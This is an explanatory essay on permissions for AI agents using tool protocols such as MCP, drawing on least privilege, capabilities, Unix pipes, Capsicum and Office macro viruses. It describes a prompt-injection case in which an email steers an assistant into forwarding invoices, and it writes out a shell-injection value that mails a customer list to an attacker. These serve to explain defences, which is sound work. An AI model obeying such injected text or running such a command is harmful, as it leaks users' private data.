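# Unplanned generality in AI agent tool protocols and its consequences for permissions

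## Tool protocols, permissions and the meaning of unplanned generality

An AI agent is a program in which a language model pursues a goal by taking actions as well as writing text. It acts through tools, which are functions in ordinary software that search a mailbox, read a file, query a database or make a payment. A tool protocol is a standard for how AI applications discover and call tools. The main example is the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic created and which OpenAI and others now support.

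A common standard lets an agent use a mail tool and a file tool in the same task even if their developers have never heard of each other. Composition means using several tools in sequence so that the output or effect of one feeds another. Much of an agent's usefulness comes from composition, but it makes permissions difficult because people usually grant them one tool at a time, while the agent works through combinations of tools, few of which anyone has considered. Computer scientists worked on versions of this problem decades before language models existed, and most of the vocabulary for it comes from them.

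### How an agent calls a tool

A language model by itself only produces text, so the application around it has to carry out any actions. In the Model Context Protocol (MCP), that application is called the host, a server is a program that offers tools and data, and a client is the host's connection to one server. In an example from the official Model Context Protocol (2026) overview, the code editor Visual Studio Code is the host. It uses one client to connect to a server for Sentry, an error-tracking service, and another to connect to a server for the files on the user's machine.

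The host first asks each server for its tool list. Each entry has a name, usually a plain-language description, and an input schema, a machine-readable statement of the arguments the tool accepts. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that covers tool calls, gives the example of a weather service whose tool, `get_weather`, takes one required argument, a string containing a city name or zip code. The host combines the entries from all its servers into a single registry and makes it available to the model.

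Suppose the user asks about the weather in New York. The model picks `get_weather` and writes a structured request with "New York" as the location. The request is only text, so nothing has happened outside the model yet. The host intercepts it, works out which server the tool belongs to and sends that server a call. The server runs the function and returns a result, such as 72°F and partly cloudy. The host then adds the result to the model's context, the text from which the model produces its next words. The model can now answer the user or call another tool. OpenAI's *MCP server*, a guide for developers, describes the same cycle of discovery, selection, execution and use of the result.

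A person may or may not get to approve a tool call. MCP's designers describe tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them automatically. The MCP specification says that a human "should" always be able to deny a call, but it doesn't require this, and each application can design its own interface. NSHipster's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, an introduction for programmers, gives a cautious example in which the application asks the user to approve a single call, with its arguments, before it fetches the weather in Portland, Oregon, for a limerick.

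MCP has no operation that passes one tool's output directly to another tool, so the model has to copy it. In the specification's shopping example, a tool called `create_basket` returns the identifier `bsk_a1b2c3`, which the model must copy into its later call to `add_item`. The July 2026 version of the protocol relies more heavily on this copying because it removed sessions. The announcement of that version (Model Context Protocol, 2026) advises developers who need continuity to have the model pass such identifiers back as arguments. The model can copy a paragraph from a private document into its next call in the same way, and that call may go to a different company's server.

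Under the design principles on the Model Context Protocol architecture page, a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or "see into" other servers, and the host controls interactions between them. This stops one server from inspecting another directly, but information can still travel between them through the model, whose context holds results from both. The principle makes the host responsible for that route but does not specify what rule the host should apply.

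### Generality that nobody planned

Before a common protocol existed, the developer of each AI application had to write a separate connection to each outside service. NSHipster describes this as an M × N problem that a standard turns into M + N. With 10 applications and 50 services, a standard reduces the pieces of connecting software from 500 to 60. This saving explains why developers want a standard, but it also means that no one designs the connection between a given application and a given service. Designing it used to give somebody an occasion to think about what the two should do together.

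Unplanned generality is the range of uses an interface allows beyond those its designers or the developers of its components had in mind. The nearest established idea is generativity, which the legal scholar Jonathan Zittrain defined in *The Generative Internet* (2006) as a technology's "overall capacity to produce unprompted change driven by large, varied, and uncoordinated audiences". The term is unrelated to "generative AI". The personal computer and the internet were the leading examples, because anyone could write a program for them and pass it on without asking the manufacturer.

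Zittrain measures a technology's generativity by four criteria. Leverage is how much difficult work the technology saves. Adaptability is how many different uses it has, or could have after modification. A plowshare is excellent for planting but poor for nearly everything else, while writing paper can also wrap fish. Ease of mastery is how little skill people need to adopt and adapt the technology. Accessibility is how easily they can get hold of it, given its price, legal restrictions and any secrecy about how it works.

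Tool protocols do well on all four. A server's author writes one interface that many applications can use, and users can ask for a new combination of tools in ordinary language. But agents go beyond Zittrain's description in one respect. On the personal computer, a person thought of the new use and wrote a program for it. An agent can put together a combination halfway through a task, use it once and never repeat it, so perhaps no author ever had that use in mind.

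"Unplanned generality" can mean two different things. In the first, designers plan for composition but leave the particular combinations open. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an example. Its architecture page lists "highly composable" servers as a goal, and its *Design Principles* rule out adding protocol features for uses that developers can build from the existing parts. Composition in MCP was planned, but the designers could not have foreseen which tools a particular user would install together.

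In the other, people find a use for a feature that its designers did not intend. Zittrain gives the example of the American telephone network in the early 1970s, where a tone of 2,600 hertz indicated that a long-distance line was idle. A toy whistle from a cereal box happened to produce the same tone. Callers who knew this dialled a toll-free number, blew the whistle to clear the line without disconnecting it, and then dialled wherever they liked without charge.

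The distinction affects what users lose when a restriction is imposed. AT&T reconfigured its network so that sounds made into a telephone could no longer control it, and ordinary callers lost nothing they had been paying for. In MCP, however, combining tools is the purpose of the protocol, so a rule that restricts combinations will remove some that users wanted.

### Least privilege, access lists and capabilities

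The standard starting point for limiting a program is the principle of least privilege. Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) says that every program and every user should work with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. The first reason it gives is that this limits the damage from an accident or error. The second, less often quoted, concerns how programs combine. Fewer privileges mean fewer possible interactions among privileged programs, so improper uses of privilege become less likely and there is less to audit when one is suspected.

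The principle is hard to apply to an agent because someone has to know what the agent's job is. A payroll program does the same job every month, but a general assistant's job depends on what the user types next. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (Iyer and Babu, 2026) approaches this problem by treating each tool the model can see as a temporary grant of authority. In its example, an agent that only has to summarise an email does not need tools that send, forward or delete email, so the system should hide those tools until the task calls for them and trusted evidence shows that the user has authorised the action.

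Privileges also need some form of record, and there are two classic ones. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, set them side by side using a small table of three users and three files:

| | /etc/passwd | /u/markm/foo | /etc/motd |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice | read | write | none |
| Bob | read | none | read |
| Carol | read | write | read |

An access-control list is a column of this table. The system stores it with the file and, when a program asks to open the file by name, looks up the requester in the list. A capability list is a row, kept with the user or program, with one entry for each thing it may use. A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and carries the right to use it, like a key that also leads its holder to the right door. *Early Capability Architectures* traces this sense of the word to a 1966 design by Dennis and Van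 Horn of MIT.

In AI, the word "capability" has other meanings besides the security one. A model's capabilities are its abilities, while "capabilities" in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) are lists of the protocol features that a client or server supports. The identifiers that a model carries between calls are generally not capabilities in the security sense either. For servers that authenticate their callers, the MCP specification describes such an identifier as "a name, not a capability", and advises the server to check the caller's authorisation every time it receives one. If a server can't authenticate callers, possession of the identifier is the only proof available, and the guidance is to make it hard to guess and limit its lifetime.

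Miller and colleagues argue that access-control lists and capability lists behave differently once a system is running, although computer scientists often treated them as equivalent because both can be read off the same table. With access-control lists, a program can name any file, whether or not it has permission to use it, while with capabilities, a program cannot even ask for a file unless it has a reference to it. They also point out that administrators can keep lists of people up to date but not lists of thousands of short-lived processes, so in practice access-control lists record the rights of user accounts, and every program a user starts gets all of that user's rights.

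Ambient authority is authority that a program has because of the account it runs under, and that any of its actions can use without the request mentioning it. If an agent runs under Alice's account, the system treats the agent's request to open her tax return as a request from Alice.

Authority in this sense is wider than permission because it covers everything a program can cause to happen, directly or through other programs. Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* criticises earlier analyses of access control for considering only how a system arranges its access rights. In an example from Miller and colleagues, Alice wants to let Bob use a resource called Carol for a while, so she gives him a reference to a program that forwards his messages to Carol, and she keeps the switch that turns it off. Bob has permission to use only the forwarder, but until Alice turns it off, he can also use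 Carol in any way the forwarder allows. An analysis of access rights alone would miss this authority. Similarly, an agent with permission to send email can cause a payment if the recipient has software that pays any invoice it receives.

### The confused deputy and prompt injection

The best-known argument for capabilities is a story about a lost billing file. Norm Hardy, who had worked at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, told it in 1988 in *The Confused Deputy* and described it as "nearly true". Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates other programs into runnable form, in a directory called SYSX. Users who ran the compiler could name a file for its debugging output. The compiler also collected statistics on how people used the programming language and wrote them to a file in SYSX. To allow this, the staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which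 let it write to any file in its own directory.

The company's billing records were also in SYSX. A user who had learned the name of the billing file gave it to the compiler as the place for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which opened the file because the compiler had the right to write in SYSX. The debugging output then overwrote the billing records.

Hardy considers the obvious repairs and finds a problem with each. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could refuse names in SYSX, but someone with legitimate access might want output in that directory. It could refuse only the billing file, but then a programmer would have to revise the compiler whenever a new sensitive file appeared. The code had been correct until the staff granted the license.

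On this account, the underlying problem was that the compiler had authority from two sources, the user and the license, and could not indicate which one it was using for a given file. A confused deputy is a program led into using its own authority for someone who lacks it. Tymshare's first remedy was a system call for switching between the two authorities, but some applications soon turned out to need more than two. With capabilities, the user would give the compiler a reference to the output file instead of its name. A user with no right to the billing file would have no reference to it to give.

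Agents can be misused in the same way through prompt injection, in which an agent treats text in the material it reads as instructions. An email might tell any AI assistant to forward the last ten invoices to an outside address. The sender has no access to the invoices and relies on the assistant's. Iyer and Babu call language-model agents "confused deputies by construction" because they act on natural-language instructions that an attacker may have contaminated.

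The comparison is good, but the remedy only partly carries over. In the Tymshare case, the user supplied one file name through one clearly marked input, so it was obvious where a capability should go. An agent receives the user's request and the attacker's sentence as text in the same context, and the model decides which file to send and to whom. If the agent already holds capabilities for the invoices and for sending mail, an injected sentence can still lead it to use both. Capabilities help to the extent that something outside the model decides which ones each task gets.

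AT&T could stop the free calls made with the telephone whistle by separating control signals from conversation, because its network existed to carry conversation. Zittrain observes that the internet's channels of communication are also its "channels of control", and that separating data from programs there would have destroyed what made it generative. Agents present much the same problem. People want an agent to act on the messages it reads, for instance by adding a proposed meeting to a calendar, so a rule that incoming text must never influence its actions would make it much less useful.

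### Single calls and whole traces

For example, an agent might have a file tool and a mail tool. Its user is willing to let it read a private salary file and email outside suppliers, but not email the salary file to a supplier. A checker that evaluates each call separately would approve both the read and the send, and the file would leave the company. This could happen without an attacker if the model misinterpreted its task.

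A trace is the complete record of an agent's calls, in order. Let A be the set of calls that the rules allow. If the checker considers only the current call, it permits every trace of calls in A, in any order and with any number of repetitions. For the salary file, it can forbid the reading or forbid the sending, but it cannot allow both calls and exclude the sequence. The checker can tell whether a call reads a private file from that call alone, but whether private data reached an outsider depends on the whole trace.

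By inspecting the message text in a call's arguments, the checker can catch a verbatim copy of a file already known to be private. But a model can also summarise the file, translate it or mention one figure from it, and the resulting message may look ordinary to anyone who does not know what the agent read earlier. A checker with that information has a memory of the trace. It can still decide on one call at a time, but its decisions also depend on earlier calls.

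Remembering the order of calls is not enough either. A rule against sending anything after reading a private file would have stopped the leak, but it would also stop a message to the same supplier about a delivery date. The user cares about where the contents of the message came from. Saltzer and Schroeder called this sort of control "putting strings on information". Their example was a tax adviser who needs a client's income figures but should not pass them to a firm that prepares mailing lists. They mention one system of the period, ADEPT, that labelled each output file with the highest classification among all the data used to create it. This is safe but imprecise, because a file gets the label even if nothing secret remains in it. In 1975 they thought such systems were rare and their mechanisms incomplete.

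The same tutorial's principle of complete mediation requires the system to check every access to every object for authority. A system can fully meet this requirement and still leak the salary file, since both calls passed their checks. Limiting which tools the model can see has a similar gap if the limits depend on each tool's own risk. Iyer and Babu sort tools into low, medium and high risk, but they acknowledge that a tool "benign in isolation may be dangerous in composition", which their tiers do not capture.

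Reviewing the combinations in advance is not a realistic alternative. An agent connected to five servers with 20 tools each has 100 tools. Order matters, because reading a file before sending a message is different from reading it afterwards, so there are 100 × 99 = 9,900 ordered pairs of different tools. Of these, 5 × 20 × 19 = 1,900 lie within a single server, where one author or team could at least in principle have considered them. The other 8,000 combine tools from different servers. There are 100 × 99 × 98 = 970,200 sequences of three different tools, and reviewing them at one minute each would take more than 16,000 hours.

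The great majority of these combinations are meaningless or harmless, such as looking up the weather and then converting a currency, and the count doesn't measure how many of the rest are dangerous. But reviewing tools individually is not enough, since an administrator who has approved all 100 has still reviewed none of the 8,000 pairs that cross from one server to another. Least privilege helps greatly when the job is known, because giving an agent only the three tools it needs leaves just six ordered pairs. Adding a sixth server with 20 more tools, by contrast, creates 4,380 new ordered pairs, of which the server's author could have anticipated only the 380 among its own tools. Under MCP, the list of tools that a server offers may also change after the user has connected to it.

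## Unix pipes and the authority of the logged-in user

Half a century before MCP, Unix users were combining programs that nobody had designed for each other. Unix is an operating system that Ken Thompson, Dennis Ritchie and their colleagues began at Bell Labs, AT&T's research laboratory, in 1969. A Unix pipe connects the output of one program to the input of another, and the person typing the command chooses which programs to connect. With few exceptions, a program may do whatever the user running it may do.

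### From a garden hose to the pipe

The idea for Unix pipes came from Doug McIlroy, who headed a small computing research department at Bell Labs. On 11 October 1964, when most of the laboratory's computing still ran in batches, he typed a one-page summary of his concerns. The first item, in the text that Bell Labs later put online, was "We should have some ways of connecting programs like garden hose". A user could then add another program whenever the data needed different processing.

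McIlroy repeatedly proposed pipes for Unix between 1970 and 1972, as he recalls in the oral history *The Origin of Pipes*. His colleagues were intrigued but did nothing. In *The Evolution of the Unix Time-sharing System*, Ritchie (1980) lists their objections, which he attributes to "a failure of imagination". McIlroy's notation put a command between its input and output files, which seemed too radical, and nobody could see how to tell those files from the command's other arguments. A model with one input and one output also seemed too confining.

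In 1972 McIlroy designed a system call named `pipe` and a notation for using it, and Thompson agreed to build it. According to McIlroy in Farrow (2016), *Interview with Doug McIlroy*, Thompson wrote the system call, added pipes to the shell (the program that reads and runs typed commands), and changed existing programs that had worked only on named files, all in one night. Until then, Ritchie writes, "no one had imagined" that anyone would want the sorting program to sort whatever arrived on its standard input. McIlroy recalls in *A Research UNIX Reader* that people wrote many one-line commands using pipes the next day.

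McIlroy had wanted composition for eight years, but nobody planned the particular combinations, and some of the first programs used in them were older than pipes. Brian Kernighan, another member of the group, says in the oral history that he began showing people combinations that "were never thought of" but were easy to compose at the keyboard. Pipes resemble MCP more than the telephone whistle because composition itself was planned.

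A few months later, while preparing a talk for a 1973 conference in London, Thompson invented the vertical bar that now marks a pipe, as McIlroy (2020) recalled in a discussion of *The UNIX Command Language (1976)*. Almost all the example commands in Thompson's paper still work in 2026, according to Stratigery's *The Unix Command Language*.

### How one format fits every program

Unix treats every file as a featureless sequence of bytes. Many systems of the time divided files into records of various kinds, and Ritchie (1977), in *The UNIX Time-sharing System*, recalls one whose Fortran compiler required "variable-length" records to be exactly 80 bytes long. A Unix text file consists of characters, with a newline at the end of each line, whichever program wrote it. Programs also use the same read and write calls for terminals, tape drives and printers as for files on disk.

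A running program, or process, refers to each open file by a small number called a file descriptor. By convention, descriptor 0 is its standard input and descriptor 1 its standard output. In the command `who | wc`, `who` lists the people logged in and `wc` counts lines, words and characters. To run it, the shell gets a pipe from the operating system and starts two processes, which inherit open files from the shell. The shell connects descriptor 1 of the first process to the writing end of the pipe and descriptor 0 of the second to the reading end. The operating system stores data written to the pipe until it is read, and makes either process wait when necessary. `wc` reads descriptor 0 exactly as it would read a file, so its author didn't have to write any code for pipes or for `who`.

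Earlier systems had similar connections, but programs needed special preparation to use them. On Multics, a larger system that Bell Labs had helped develop, programmers had to write connecting modules solely for that purpose. The Dartmouth Time-Sharing System had "communication files" that looked like ordinary files at only one end. The program at the other end had to be written for them, as John, a contributor to a Unix history mailing list, explains. Ritchie thought the genius of the Unix pipeline was that people built it from the same commands they used on their own every day.

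A spelling checker shows what this made possible. Ritchie's group already had three programs that could translate characters, sort a file while dropping duplicate lines, and print the lines of one sorted file that were missing from another. Take the text "the cat saw teh other cat":

1. The first program turns the spaces into newlines, which puts each word on its own line.
2. The second sorts the lines and drops the repeated "cat", leaving "cat", "other", "saw", "teh" and "the".
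3. The third compares this list with a sorted dictionary and prints the only word not in it, "teh".

None of these programs has anything to do with spelling. McIlroy lists `comm`, a program of the third kind, among the tools from a statistical study of English text. The group had to write only one small program, which generated plausible derivatives of the dictionary's words so the checker would not report every plural as a mistake.

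The common format had drawbacks. A heading above the output of `who` would make `who | wc` count one user too many, so Unix programs print very little besides their results. Error messages at first went down the pipe mixed with the data, until Ritchie gave them a separate output. A more serious problem for permissions is that a stream of bytes carries no record of where it came from or whether it is secret. The sorting program can handle both a dictionary and a payroll because nothing marks them as different, but this also leaves the system with nothing to check when the payroll moves from one program to the next.

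### One user's authority at every stage

*On the Security of UNIX* (Ritchie, 1977) describes how Unix checks permissions when a process opens a file. Every process carries the identification number of a user, normally the one who started it. The system compares this number with the file's owner and consults nine bits, which separately allow reading, writing and execution by the owner, the owner's group and everyone else. The check does not depend on which program the process is running. A sorting program in a pipeline needs only to read its input and write its output, but it could also open or overwrite any file that its user could, an arrangement known as ambient authority.

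Connecting two such programs adds no authority. If Alice cannot read a file, no stage of her pipeline can read it. Kernighan points out that people could already do most of what pipes do by saving one program's output in a file and giving that file to the next. But a pipe makes it much easier to use existing authority in a new way. Suppose only Alice may read the file `salaries`, and she types `cat salaries | mail bob`. The `cat` command copies the file into the pipe, and `mail` sends the contents to Bob. Every check succeeds, as it did for the agent with the salary file. Bob still cannot read the original, but its permission bits do not apply to his copy.

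This was tolerable because Alice had typed the command. She had chosen both programs, the file and the recipient, and she could have retyped the salaries into a message anyway. A mistake would mostly have damaged her own files. The early users also had little reason to suspect their programs, since they worked together in one attic room and had written most of the programs themselves. Ritchie says that Unix was not developed with security, "in any realistic sense, in mind" and that his group had "not been faced with malicious users".

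The exception to user-level authority was set-user-ID, a feature that makes a program run with the rights of its owner instead of the person who starts it. A game can use it to update a file of high scores that players cannot edit themselves. An early mail program used it to run as the "super-user", an administrator account that the permission bits do not restrict, so that it could deliver mail into protected directories. Anyone could get this program to send them another user's private file.

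Ritchie describes a worse attack on the same program. Unix kept its list of accounts in a text file, the password file. An attacker could create a link to this file under the name of a mailbox, then mail that mailbox a line that would allow a login as super-user. The mail program had the authority to write to the password file, so it added the line, and the attacker could then log in. This is a confused deputy, described 11 years before Hardy's article. The combination was also unplanned. The mail program's output could become the login program's input because both used plain text.

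### When a stranger supplies the text

User-level authority becomes much more dangerous when someone other than the user can write part of a command. Imagine a website that emails a leaflet to any address a visitor enters. Its programmer inserts the address into the command `cat leaflet | mail ADDRESS` and passes the result to a shell. One visitor enters this as an address:

`eve@example.com; cat customers | mail eve@example.com`

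A semicolon separates commands in the shell, so the shell sends the leaflet and then runs a second pipeline that sends Eve the customer list. If the website's account can read that list, the system allows this. Both pipelines use the same two programs and the same account, but a stranger chose the file in the second. Programmers call this attack shell injection.

The programmer can prevent this by starting the mail program directly and passing the whole address as one argument, so that no shell interprets the semicolon. This fix depends on a clear boundary between commands and data, which a language model's context lacks. An agent that uses a shell instead of MCP also runs its commands with the full authority of its account, unless something else restricts it.

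Hostile data can also do harm without reaching a shell. A web browser processes pages, scripts, images and video from many untrusted sources, and on a conventional system it has access to all its user's files. An attacker who finds a fault in the image decoder may gain the same access. The nine permission bits are little help because they protect users from each other. Anderson (2017), in *A Comparison of Unix Sandboxing Techniques*, argues that people now need finer control, such as being able to share a single contact.

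### Capsicum turns descriptors into capabilities

Capsicum is the best-documented attempt to add capabilities to Unix without replacing it. Watson, Anderson and colleagues presented it in *Capsicum* (2010) and built it into FreeBSD, a free descendant of Unix. It uses file descriptors, which Unix already had. Unix checks permission when a process opens a file, and the resulting descriptor then serves as proof of access. A process cannot forge a descriptor, but it can pass one to another process.

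Capsicum adds two mechanisms. The first is capability mode, which a process enters by calling `cap_enter` and can never leave. In this mode, the process cannot open a file by its ordinary path, contact a network address or refer to an arbitrary process by its process ID. It can still use the descriptors it already holds and any that other processes pass to it. Any processes it starts are also in capability mode.

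The second mechanism restricts those descriptors. With an ordinary Unix descriptor, a process that opened a file only for reading may still be able to change the file's permission bits. Capsicum wraps the descriptor in a capability that lists the allowed operations, chosen from about 60. A process can make a narrower capability from it but never a broader one. A capability can also cover a directory, so a process with one for `/lib` can open the files under `/lib` but cannot use it to reach files elsewhere, such as the password file.

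Watson and colleagues converted four programs:

| Program | Purpose | Code changed or added |
|---|---|---|
| tcpdump | displays network traffic | 2 lines, or about 10 with tighter limits on the terminal |
| dhclient | obtains network settings | 2 lines |
| gzip | compresses files | 409 lines, about 16% of the program |
| Chromium | web browser | about 100 lines |

The small line counts depend heavily on how the programs were already built. tcpdump opens everything it needs at the start and then processes packets in a loop, so the programmers could put `cap_enter` just before the loop. But this broke tcpdump's lookup of computer names, because the library code opened a configuration file only when it first needed it, and by then capability mode blocked the request. The programmers had to send the lookups to a separate local service. Chromium needed only 100 lines because its developers had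 already divided it into processes with different duties.

gzip had no such division. The programmers split it into a part that opens files and a sandboxed part that compresses them, with access to just one input and one output at a time. At first the new version seemed faster than the old one, but only because they had forgotten to pass the user's chosen compression level to the sandboxed part.

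The performance overhead was low. Operations on a restricted descriptor took about 0.06 microseconds longer, which made the worst affected of the tested calls 10% slower. tcpdump and dhclient showed no noticeable slowdown. Starting gzip in its sandbox took an extra 2.37 milliseconds. That was a large proportion of the total time for a tiny file, but once files reached about 512 kilobytes, the sandboxed and unsandboxed versions were within 5% of each other. Watson and colleagues consider the difficulty of programming the largest problem, since developers must divide a program into communicating parts and then work out whether they chose the right division.

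Sandboxing each stage of a pipeline could avoid some of this work. In Mark Seaborn's Plash design, the shell does this while keeping the user's full authority itself. A sorting program would then receive only its input and output, with almost no change to its code. Watson and colleagues had begun to explore this on Capsicum, but they note that gzip also does jobs outside pipelines that need wider access, and that moving the logic for those jobs into the shell could be just as awkward.

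Such a shell would keep most of the generality of pipes, because users could still connect any program to any other. It would also stop a faulty stage from reaching files outside the pipeline. But it would not stop Alice from mailing the salaries to Bob, or the website from sending Eve the customer list, since in both cases the command names the file and the mail program.

Capsicum was an experimental option in FreeBSD 9.0 and became available by default in version 10.0, according to the University of Cambridge's *Capsicum* page, but few application developers have used it. In a 2023 search, Alhindi and Hallett (*Sandboxing Adoption in Open Source Ecosystems*, 2024) found that 43 of FreeBSD's 30,763 packages (0.14%) called it directly. Their count excludes the core system, which matters because Watson and colleagues had started with core utilities. But use was also low in the core system.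 In a separate check of a newly installed machine, only 3 of the 47 processes running after startup used Capsicum.

On OpenBSD, a related system, the figure was 33 of 36. Its developers use a simpler mechanism, in which a program declares the broad kinds of operation it will need. They also have a reputation for putting security first. Among OpenBSD's add-on packages, though, direct use was only about 1.5%.

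In one server program that Alhindi and Hallett examined, Capsicum took 28 lines of code, against 96 for OpenBSD's mechanisms and 549 for a Linux one, so the amount of code does not explain the low numbers. They think a more likely obstacle is that developers have to know everything a program will need and may have to restructure it. FreeBSD has tried to help with a library that, according to its manual, opens files and network connections for sandboxed programs. Alhindi and Hallett suggest restricting programs by default, as the JavaScript platform Deno does, so that developers have to request any access their programs need.

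## Office macros and documents that run programs

Microsoft Office documents could contain programs, so a user who opened a letter or a budget could start a program written by a stranger, and it would run with the user's permissions. A Unix user who typed a pipeline, by contrast, chose the programs in it.

### From recorded keystrokes to a programming language

A macro is a series of commands that an application carries out as one. In the simplest kind, the application records a user's keystrokes and plays them back later, which helps someone who formats the same report every week. Many applications also let users write macros in a special language. In *Macro Viruses*, a series of articles for the trade magazine Virus Bulletin, Muttik (1999) wrote that the newer languages were "as complex as general purpose programming languages".

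Word 6.0 had WordBasic, a version of the teaching language BASIC with hundreds of extra commands for working with documents. Excel 5.0 had a related language, Visual Basic for Applications (VBA). In January 1997 Microsoft released Office 97, in which all the main applications used VBA. A macro written for one application could now work in another, and PowerPoint got macros for the first time. Muttik reports that the first PowerPoint viruses followed.

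Microsoft planned for users to automate their documents with macros, but macros could also act outside those documents. Krukov (1996), in *In the Beginning was the Word*, explains that both WordBasic and Excel's language could call routines in Windows' own libraries, which gave macros access to all the computer's resources. A macro could therefore delete files or start other programs if its user could.

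Macros could also run without the user starting them. Word and Excel ran a macro with a certain name whenever a user opened the document that contained it. In Word, a macro named after a menu command replaced that command. A firm could use this to stamp a reference number on every letter its staff saved, and a virus could use it to copy itself into those letters. The US Department of Energy's computer incident team, CIAC, regarded automatic running as the feature that made macro viruses possible. Its bulletin *Winword Macro Viruses* (1996) criticized Word for allowing automatic running by default and making it difficult to turn off. Users could not disable the replacement of menu commands.

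### From a demonstration to an epidemic

In December 1994 the researcher Joel McNamara wrote a virus in Word's macro language to show that it could be done. McNamara's *Document Macro Viruses* argued that powerful macro languages, combined with macros that run automatically, threatened people "who have been taught that data files cannot harm your system". McNamara infected the document containing the paper so that readers could try the virus themselves, and made the virus announce each step in a dialog box.

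Concept, the first macro virus to spread among the public, appeared in the summer of 1995. When a user opened an infected document, Concept copied itself into the template that Word loads at startup, and from there into other documents as the user saved them. The first time it ran, it displayed a box containing the digit 1. It did no deliberate damage, but it could make documents difficult to save, as The Christian Science Monitor's *New Kind of Virus Riles Fanfare for Windows 95* reported. Microsoft called it a "prank macro" (Ducklin, 2022, *That didn’t last!*). It soon became the most widespread virus up to that time, as Muttik recounts.

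Concept spread widely because people shared documents much more than programs. CIAC noted that documents move from machine to machine as colleagues write and edit them, and that most users did not scan them for viruses. The same macro could also run on both Windows and Macintosh. By September 1999 there were about 5,000 macro viruses. Some had no author. Muttik found that around 200 variants of one virus, Npad, arose because Word 6.0 sometimes corrupted macros when copying them, and many of the damaged copies still worked.

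### How much the Lotus comparison shows

Lotus 1-2-3, an earlier and widely used spreadsheet, also had macros, and researchers had worked out how to write a virus for it. An editorial on Concept in Virus Bulletin (1995) noted that the idea dated from before the 1990s. Yet viruses were never a problem for Lotus users. Muttik attributes this to Lotus's simple macro language, which could reach files only through the program's menus. A virus would have had to open those menus on the screen, where the user could watch it spread.

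The two products also differed in how many people used them and how those people exchanged files, so the comparison does not show that a weaker language would have spared Office its viruses. The word processor AmiPro had macros powerful enough for somebody to write a virus, but Krukov points out that people did not exchange AmiPro documents widely. A product can therefore escape an epidemic even if its macro language is dangerous. CIAC's explanation differs from Muttik's in emphasising automatic running rather than access to files.

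PowerPoint is a cleaner comparison because it is the same product before and after it gained macros, but it shows only the obvious point that macro viruses need macros. The Lotus case supports the narrower conclusion that a macro has trouble spreading unnoticed if it can reach files only by a route the user can see. It does not show how much of the difference between Lotus and Office came from this limit.

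*The Rule of Least Power* (Berners-Lee and Mendelsohn, 2006), a finding for the web standards body W3C, advises publishers to choose the least powerful language suitable for the purpose, because the more a language can compute, the harder it is to tell what a program in it will do. With a full programming language, the only way to find out is often to run the program. Simpler languages are usually easier to secure, and their security problems are easier to find.

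They also argue that people can do more with information when it is written in a less powerful language. If a weather service publishes its readings as plain data, a reader's software can tabulate them, average them or combine them with other data. If it publishes a program that draws a weather map, a search engine may not recognise that the page is about weather. On this argument, macros let document authors do more but could limit what other people's software can do with the documents.

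Applying the rule to Office requires care. It concerns publishing on the web, and Mendelsohn (2012) objected when readers turned it into a general command to choose the least powerful way of doing anything. The finding also warns that an overly limited language leads to clumsy workarounds. The rule is mainly about computing power, while much of the trouble with macros came from their authority. A macro that deletes a folder can be two lines long and easy to analyse. A complicated macro may be impossible to predict, but it cannot send anybody's files away if it can only change the numbers in its own spreadsheet. Lotus limited both what macros could express and what they could reach, and Muttik's explanation depends on the limit on reach.

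### Melissa borrows the mail program

Concept spread only when people shared infected documents, but Melissa, which appeared on 26 March 1999, emailed them automatically. CERT (1999), the computer security centre at Carnegie Mellon University, described how it worked. When a user opened an infected Word document with macros enabled, Melissa used the mail program Outlook to send an infected document to the first 50 entries in every address book the user could read. If an entry was a mailing list, everyone on the list got a copy. Each message carried the user's name and text saying that it contained a document the recipient had asked for.

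By Monday Melissa had reached more than 100,000 computers. CERT had first-hand reports from over 300 organisations, one of which received 32,000 infected messages in 45 minutes. Some organisations had to take their mail systems offline. Melissa apparently did no direct damage to computers (Los Angeles Times, 1999), but it could leak confidential information, because the document it sent from an infected computer might be one the victim had written.

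Melissa could spread without exploiting any new vulnerability, because Word allowed macros to control other programs, Outlook allowed other programs to send mail, and the user had permission to do both. A legitimate macro might take each of these steps to send invoices to a list of customers. But in Melissa, a stranger with no right to use the victim's address book had combined them. Word was in effect a confused deputy, because it used its user's authority on behalf of whoever had written the document.

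The Macintosh is a better test than Lotus of what this combination contributed. On a Macintosh, Melissa could infect Word 98 documents but could not send mail. CERT expected it to spread more slowly on those machines because it would again depend on people sharing files.

Microsoft eventually restricted the link between the programs. Seltzer (2009), in *10 Years With Melissa, the Worm that Changed the World*, writes that it acted only after another mail worm, ILoveYou, struck the year after Melissa. It then updated Outlook to block the basic method both worms had used. The update limited how the programs could be combined, but macros still ran and Outlook still sent mail. Worm writers soon switched to sending messages directly over the internet's mail protocol, without Outlook.

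### Why asking the user failed

Microsoft began warning users about macros in Word 7.0a, an update to the Office 95 version. In Word 97, a user opening a document with macros could disable them (the default), enable them or leave the document closed. The user could also turn off the warning permanently, and the Melissa virus did the same by lowering the macro security settings as soon as it ran.

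People could learn from the warning that a document contained macros, but not what the macros would do. Most users could not have judged the code even if they had seen it, and a useful budget spreadsheet produced the same warning as a virus. Muttik also describes Office 97 files that still set off the warning after their macros were gone.

Criminals also controlled what the user was reading when Office asked whether to enable macros. They filled the document with instructions for enabling its contents, often with an arrow pointing at the button, as Ducklin recounts. Microsoft's advice to users lists some of the pretexts, such as cancelling an order or reading a legal document. Someone who wanted to see an unexpected invoice had a reason to click yes, but could not let the macro display the invoice without also allowing everything else a macro could do. An enabled macro got access to "the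 identity, documents, and network of the person who enabled it", a Microsoft security manager said in the company's 2022 announcement. Approval prompts for AI agents can have the same weakness if the user sees a request but not its consequences.

Later versions of Office left fewer decisions to users. Word 2000 had a high security setting that ignored macros unless they were digitally signed by a source the user had chosen to trust. A signature identifies who signed a macro and shows that it hasn't been changed since, but doesn't limit what the macro can do. Office 2010 added Protected View, which opens files from the internet in a restricted, read-only mode. Users could still leave it with a click to edit the document.

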